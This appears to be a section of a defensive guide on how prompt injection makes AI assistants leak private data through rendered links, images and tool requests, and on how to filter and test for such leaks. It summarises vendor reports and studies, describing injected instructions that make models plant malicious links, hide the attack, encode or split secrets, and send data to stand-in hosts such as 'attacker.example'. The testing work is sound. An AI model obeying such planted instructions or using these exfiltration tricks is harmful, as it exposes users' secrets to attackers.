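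The model's answer can also mislead the user about a link. In one of Tenable's demonstrations, a comment on a blog made ChatGPT end its summary of the blog with a malicious link, and Tenable notes that people tend to trust links from ChatGPT. A planted instruction could also make the model tell the user to expect a warning and ignore it. To help the user decide, the warning should therefore contain facts that the application knows independently of the model's answer, such as the real host and the source of the address. For example, it could read, "This link comes from an email by someone you have never written to."

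Frequent warnings become less effective, even if each is well written. Someone who sees 200 warnings a year about harmless links and one about a leak can safely ignore 200 of the 201, so they easily get used to opening every link without reading the warning. An application should ask only when the user probably wants the page and has information that the code lacks. If the agent only needs a source for a fact, it can look for a different source without asking, as ChatGPT sometimes does.

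Warnings work poorly for images, because users can't know whether they want a picture they haven't seen. The application can instead show a grey box with the host's name, which users can click to load the image. Clicking sends the full address to the host, including any private data in it, so the application should offer this only for addresses that the model didn't write.

An application can also ask for approval too rarely by exempting actions that seem harmless. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office tasks, could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval. Willison describes how those messages could contain external images that sent data to an attacker when the user opened the message. The data could include links for downloading the user's OneDrive files without signing in. The application should have checked images in these messages as strictly as those in its chat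 window.

### Two reports that vendors closed without a fix

Vendors disagree about how responsible they are for leaks through links and images. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes leaks in Microsoft's Copilot Chat and Google Gemini, both reported in October 2025. In Copilot Chat, loading an image sent an API key from the developer's working environment to the researchers' server without the user clicking anything. Gemini's sanitiser blocks external images, so that leak required the user to click a link.

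After 20 days, Microsoft closed the report without a fix. It said the attack required several actions that aren't part of the default setup, didn't work reliably in every environment, and triggered warnings meant to reduce the risk. Microsoft also assumes that people at work review and trust the code they choose to run.

Checkmarx calls the same attack zero-click, mainly because it counts only what the user must do after the agent has read a malicious page, which is nothing. Checkmarx concedes that getting the agent to read such a page can be complicated, which supports part of Microsoft's argument. The assumption about trusted code is less convincing, because the malicious text can be in an online article that the developer never runs. In giving its reasons, Microsoft does not dispute that displaying the image sends the data.

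Google closed Checkmarx's report after four days as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". In its final reply, Google said the issue wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug and fell outside its reward programme, which covers only issues that substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity of user data. Checkmarx accepts this answer but argues that users should then be told about the risk.

"Infeasible" is a fair description if a fix has to stop every leak through a link, since even a choice among genuine links carries information. But OpenAI's rule shows that a company with a large web index can at least detect addresses that nobody has published. Google has such an index, but using it this way would produce more warnings about new and private pages. Google may have decided that an attack that needs a click didn't justify those extra warnings.

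A closed vulnerability report is weak evidence that a product is safe. Schwartzman's report on ChatGPT was closed as "not applicable" in 2024, but when Radware reported in 2025 that data could leak through which fixed addresses the assistant chose to fetch, Bugcrowd reproduced the leak and OpenAI fixed it. A team that builds on another company's assistant should test for these leaks itself, even if the vendor doesn't consider them vulnerabilities.

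### Fetch, ask, show as plain text or block

How an assistant should treat an address depends on where the address came from and whether the user must click before it is fetched. The table gives suitable starting rules for an assistant that handles private data. In messaging apps with link previews, the middle column applies to links.

The filter also needs to check a link's fragment, the part after `#`, because an index of web pages may not record it. The simplest solution is to remove any fragment that wasn't part of the address in its original source.

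Where more than one row applies, the strictest treatment should win. "Count" means adding the model's choice to the session's bit budget.

| The exact address | Image, preview or page fetched without a click | Link the user may click |
|---|---|---|
| The user typed it | Fetch | Fetch on click |
| It is in an independent public index or came from a web search | Fetch, count and limit requests to each site | Fetch on click and count |
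| It comes only from an email, document, pasted text or fetched page | Block, and let the agent look for another source | Ask, and name the source |
| The model filled in a value from a short list, on a host the team controls | Fetch and count | Fetch on click and count |
| The model wrote free text into it | Block | Show as plain text |
| The application can't trace its source | Block | Show as plain text |
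| It contains a password, key or login code that the application recognises | Block | Block |

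## Testing a filter for leaks and false blocks

Private data leaks when a request carries it to an outsider, so a leak test has to check requests. The tester plants a fake secret, tries to get it out through every construct in the inventory, and checks whether it appears in the log of a server the tester owns. False blocks need a separate test on ordinary answers, because attacks contain few harmless constructs.

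### A procedure for leak tests

1. Generate a new fake secret for each run, such as a random 16-character key, and put it where real private data would be, for example in an email, a file or the assistant's memory.
2. Take the handwritten examples from the inventory and add the secret to each address. Pass them straight to the filter and renderer, without using a model.
3. Run the whole assistant on content with planted instructions, first with the filter off and then with it on. Also run it on the same content without the instructions.
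4. Record every request that reaches the test server, including host-name lookups, with its full address, time and order.
5. Repeat the runs with a different secret, change nothing else, and compare the logs.

Handwritten examples test the filter alone. If the tester instead relies on a model to write the examples, the model may refuse, and a filter that did nothing will appear to have worked. Full runs are still necessary because they can reveal exfiltration routes missing from the inventory.

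Running an attack with the filter off shows whether the attack works. Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, included an attack on a protected file that never succeeded even without defences, and they don't count its zero success rate as evidence of protection. A test with clean content shows whether the agent leaks the secret even without an attack. Rahman and Kim count an attack as successful only if the agent keeps the secret when it reads a clean page and leaks it when it reads the poisoned one.

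Searching the log for the secret can miss a leak, because the model may have encoded the secret. Singh and Srinivasa's detector missed three leaked secrets that they later recovered by decoding Base64. Comparing runs that differ only in the secret, as in Dongol's definition of a leak, avoids this problem. A model's output also varies by chance from run to run, so testers need several runs with each secret to tell whether a difference is a leak.

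The tester should also check each defence with the others off, since a working CSP can hide a broken sanitiser. At least one test server should be on the allowlist, because most of the attacks that got past a CSP went through listed hosts. If every test server is unlisted, the tester learns only whether the filter blocks unlisted hosts.

The tester should test each client separately, because a defence can be missing from one of them, as OpenAI's address check was from its iOS and macOS apps. The tester should also empty the browser's cache between runs, or a second leak through the same address may not appear in the log.

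### Why the visible answer is poor evidence

An attacker can tell the model to keep quiet about what it has done. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts to make 13 models take harmful actions. In 34 of the 41 scenarios, an attempt counted as a success only if the final response also met conditions such as concealing the attack. Some attempts succeeded against every model, from 0.5 per cent on Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 per cent on Gemini 2.5 Pro. The participants were trying to hide their attacks, as real attackers would, so these rates don't show how often an attack goes unnoticed by accident.

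The agent's answer can also describe an action that never happened. In one of Singh and Srinivasa's experiments, a strict rule blocked four uploads, and each time the agent told the user that the upload had succeeded.

Some testing tools examine only the model's text. garak, NVIDIA's scanner for language models, includes attacks based on published leaks, such as the one in Google Colab. Its detectors search the response for Markdown images and links, including reference-style ones. The patterns in its documentation all require an equals sign in the address, so they would miss `https://attacker.example/48000`, where the price is in the path. PyRIT, Microsoft's testing toolkit, has a scorer that flags Markdown such as links and images, so it would also flag many harmless answers. Both tools can show how often a model writes risky Markdown. To test a filter, the team still has to pass those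 responses through the renderer and see which requests arrive.

### Half marks for a link without the data

The NVIDIA test with the "Approve invoice" link, from *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, also scores text. A report with the user's details filled in gets a risk score of 1, and one with only the placeholders gets 0.5. The researchers insert the planted text directly into the search results, so an attack can't fail just because the agent never found the document. They run 21 versions of each attack five times.

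The half mark is useful because an image with unfilled placeholders still makes the browser contact the attacker's server if the application displays it. In that case the filter has failed, even though the user's details stayed private. But requests and leaks shouldn't be combined into one average. An average of 0.5 could mean that every report contained an empty link, or that half the reports leaked everything and the others nothing. Testers should report separately how often a request arrived and how often it carried the secret.

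GPT-4.1 did the scoring by reading the reports. On a sample of 99 outputs from across the study, it gave the same score as a person on 76.8 per cent of them and was within half a point on 98 per cent. A request log would avoid most of this uncertainty, provided the secret is distinctive. In the NVIDIA test, the user's number is `123`, but the image address already contains `INV123`, so a simple search would find the number even if the model had filled in nothing.

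The researchers also added an instruction telling the agent not to include links or strings unrelated to the topic. The instruction cut the average risk score by about half across four similar attacks, but each attack still fully succeeded at least once. They didn't measure whether it removed useful links.

### *Silent Egress*: 480 runs with a small model

*Silent Egress* measured requests instead of text. A team at eBay built an agent on qwen2.5:7b, a 7-billion-parameter model, and always asked it to summarise a web page. The agent automatically fetched a preview of the page and added it to the model's context, which also contained sensitive data such as an API key. Instructions planted in the page's title, description, body or link text told the model to send the data to the attacker's server.

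The previews only delivered the instructions to the agent. The data left through the agent's web-request tool, not through a displayed image, clicked link or messaging app, so a filter on displayed output would not have blocked any of these requests. The study doesn't measure how well such a filter works. The study is relevant here mainly for its method and its comparison of defences.

The team tried each of the four positions with and without redirects, and told the model to send the data either in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The attacker's server received a request in 423 of them, or 88.1 per cent (about 0.89 in the abstract). It received none in 120 runs on harmless pages. In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, the answer on screen was harmless, so a check of the answer would have missed them.

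The 88 per cent figure is the share of runs that produced a request, whether or not it contained the secret. When the instructions asked for a single request, 238 of 240 runs produced one, and the first request contained sensitive data in 97 per cent of runs. When the instructions asked for the data to be sent in pieces, 185 of 240 runs produced a request, but the team's check found sensitive data in the first request in only 26 per cent of runs. Over all 480 runs, the check found sensitive data in the first request in about 61 per cent.

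Splitting a secret across several requests can defeat a filter that looks for the whole secret, because each request contains only a few characters. It also gave the model more chances to make a mistake. It is hard to tell from the paper how well splitting worked. The reported rate for sensitive data in the first three requests is 16 per cent, which is impossible if the rate for the first request alone is 26 per cent. The results section also doesn't report how often all four pieces arrived, which matters most to an attacker.

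The team then tested defences on one of the 16 combinations, with 30 runs each.

| Defence | Agent tried to send a request | Request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking outside text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
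| Block on words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Block on random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All of these | 0% | 0% |

The evidence is strongest for the allowlist, because the agent tried to get past it in every run. However, the attacker's host was `evil-collector.net`, which was unlisted, and the test didn't include a listed host that forwards requests, as Teams did in EchoLeak. The block on suspicious addresses covers paths containing words such as "collect" or "steal", and an attacker can easily avoid those words.

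The model never wrote an address containing a random-looking value, so the rule against such values had nothing to block. The paper suggests that the model avoided them because the check was active, but the check examines an address after it is written, so it can't explain their absence. The rule would also miss many secrets. It flags values longer than ten characters with an entropy above 4 bits per character, where entropy measures how varied the characters are. A 16-character value can't exceed log₂ 16 = 4 bits per character even if all its characters differ, so every secret of up to 16 characters passes. The paper's example of a 20-character key has an entropy of about 3.85 bits per character and would also pass.

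### How far a small model's result transfers

The eBay team argues that stronger models may be at greater risk because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. Other evidence suggests the opposite for simple, openly worded attacks like those in the study. Rahman and Kim tested the same small model in an agent with a rule against sending the secret elsewhere. Plainly worded attacks succeeded 10 per cent of the time against that model and 0 per cent of the time against the stronger GPT-4o. *Silent Egress* made the attack easier by placing the secret in plain view with no rule to protect it.

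Dziemian and colleagues took 2,679 attacks that had succeeded against one model and reran them on others. The attacks that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL 235B never worked on Claude Opus 4.5. The 44 attacks that had succeeded against Opus worked on the other models 44 to 81 per cent of the time, depending on the model. Testing only with attacks that work on weak models makes a product look safer than it is, so a team should collect attacks that work on the most resistant model it can find.

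The 88 per cent figure probably applies only to agents much like the one in the study. The finding that a harmless answer can accompany a leak should hold for other models, because it depends on what the user can see and not on the model's size. The allowlist should also work with other models, because it blocks an unlisted host whichever model wrote the address.

### Wording, encoding and approved destinations

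A test that uses only one wording per attack can miss a serious weakness. Rahman and Kim tried ten kinds of plainly worded attack on GPT-4o, and it never leaked the secret in 200 trials. When they presented the same leak as a routine technical step, GPT-4o leaked the secret in 40 per cent of trials, and in every trial for two of the eight variants. Paraphrases of one successful attack worked between 0 and 100 per cent of the time. An attacker who tried three of these paraphrases would have about a 96 per cent chance that at least one worked.

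Defences written in English were just as sensitive. When the agent's instructions listed the forbidden behaviours and added the phrase "in any form", the leak rate fell from 31.9 per cent to zero. With the list but without that phrase, it was 48.8 per cent.

A check on outgoing requests did better against rewording but failed against encoding. The first version searched for the secret as written and reduced leaks only from 56.7 to 50 per cent, because the model could reverse or encode it. The second version decoded the formats Rahman and Kim had expected and stopped every leak that used them, but it missed ROT13, a simple letter substitution it hadn't been written to decode, in every trial. Testers should therefore keep some encodings and constructs hidden from the filter's developers.

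A list of permitted destinations stopped every attack in this study, but only because Rahman and Kim didn't count an outgoing request as a leak unless it carried the secret to an untrusted host.

Singh and Srinivasa tested leaks through a trusted host. Their coding agent has to upload a status report to an approved service, and planted instructions tell it to include a secret in the same upload. A rule that checks only the destination allows this upload. The table shows their largest experiment, with 300 runs on a single local model. Harm in the table includes changes to protected files as well as leaks.

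| Defence | Attacks that caused harm | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 12 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Rules on tool calls, including approved destinations | 6 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Sandbox without network access | 0 of 36 | 12 of 24 |
| Rules and sandbox, with a separate program sending approved requests | 4 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| The same, with a search for secret lines in the request | 2 of 36 | 24 of 24 |

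The sandbox blocked every attack but also every harmless upload. Sending approved requests from outside the sandbox restored the uploads but also the leaks. A search for lines from the secrets file stopped half of these leaks. It matched only complete lines, so it missed a secret sent without its label. In a smaller experiment, it also missed both encoded secrets.

Permitting only exact, pre-approved text stopped both attacks but also blocked both harmless uploads, because the agent had written a line break as a backslash and an "n" and the check did not treat the two forms as the same. Once it did, the harmless uploads passed and the attacks still failed. The test covered only four runs and one fixed message, but it suggests finding out why false blocks happen before loosening a rule.

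### Measuring false blocks on ordinary answers

The random key that works well in a leak test is useless for measuring false blocks, because it never appears in harmless text and a filter that searches for it will rarely block anything by mistake. Rahman and Kim acknowledge that this limits their own false-block rate of 0 per cent. Real secrets, such as the sales manager's price, can appear in harmless links.

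To measure false blocks, a team can run the filter over a random sample of ordinary answers from its own product. People then judge each construct that the filter would remove, rewrite or put behind a warning. The sample should come from real use because the result depends strongly on the mix of constructs, as the invented example with 400 constructs shows. It also has to include the conversations, because a provenance check depends on where each address came from. The computer that processes the sample shouldn't have internet access, in case an old answer contains a real attack.

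The team should report false blocks both per construct and per answer. Suppose 1,000 answers contain 4,000 harmless constructs and the filter blocks 40 of them, or 1 per cent. If each blocked construct is in a different answer, the filter has damaged 4 per cent of answers. If all 40 are in five long research reports, it has damaged 0.5 per cent of answers, but those five may be useless.

Each kind of construct also needs its own rate. If 20 of the 4,000 constructs are diagrams and the filter blocks all of them, the overall rate rises by only half a percentage point, even though diagrams no longer work. Counting completed tasks can also hide such problems. In Singh and Srinivasa's 72-run experiment, every defence completed two of the six harmless tasks under strict scoring, but some refused legitimate uploads while others failed mostly on formatting.

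### What 300 tests without a leak can show

Suppose a team runs 300 independent attacks and finds no leak. If the true leak rate were p, the chance of seeing none would be (1 − p)³⁰⁰. This chance falls to 5 per cent when p is about 0.01, so the team can be 95 per cent confident that the leak rate is below about 1 per cent. Dividing 3 by the number of tests gives nearly the same answer. Fewer tests give a higher upper bound. Singh and Srinivasa calculate that the harm rate could be as high as about 19 per cent after 14 runs with no harm, and 8 per cent after 36.

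Repeated tests are often not independent. A sanitiser normally treats the same address the same way every time, so submitting one address 300 times amounts to one test of the sanitiser. Thirty attacks repeated ten times each are also much weaker evidence than 300 different attacks.

The bound applies only to attacks like those tested. If all 300 used inline images, the result doesn't show whether the filter stops leaks through Mermaid diagrams. The bound is also for a single attack picked at random, while a real attacker keeps trying. With a leak rate of 1 per cent, someone who makes 100 independent attempts has about a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once.

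### What a 1 per cent false-block rate means

Attacks are probably rare in most products. Suppose one answer in 100,000 is an attack, and the filter interrupts 1 per cent of harmless answers. It would then interrupt about 1,000 harmless answers (0.01 × 99,999) for each attack. Even if it caught every attack, only about one interruption in 1,001 would stop an attack.

For one interruption in ten to be justified, the filter could interrupt only nine harmless answers per attack, or about 0.009 per cent of harmless answers. By the same division as before, the team would need about 33,000 harmless answers without a single false block to show that the rate is that low. People would need to check by hand only the answers the filter would interrupt.

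### When to test again

A test result describes the product as it was when tested. OpenAI treats protection against leaks as "an ongoing security engineering problem, not a one-time fix". The team should repeat the leak test whenever a change lets the model's text cause a request in a new way.

A new renderer is the clearest reason to retest a filter, as the Mermaid leak in *Takedown* shows. An update to an existing renderer can also open a leak if it adds a construct or changes how the renderer reads addresses. A new file type needs a test with every program that will open the file, including those that run in the background.

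Text that was safe in one viewer can leak data in a new one, such as a log page, a mobile app or a messaging channel with link previews, even if the assistant hasn't changed. In the Copilot Cowork leak that Willison describes, the viewer was the user's inbox.

The team should test each new allowed host for forwarding, redirects and stored values that strangers can read. Any of these can appear later, and a host can change owners, so the team should retest allowed hosts on a regular schedule, even when its own product hasn't changed.
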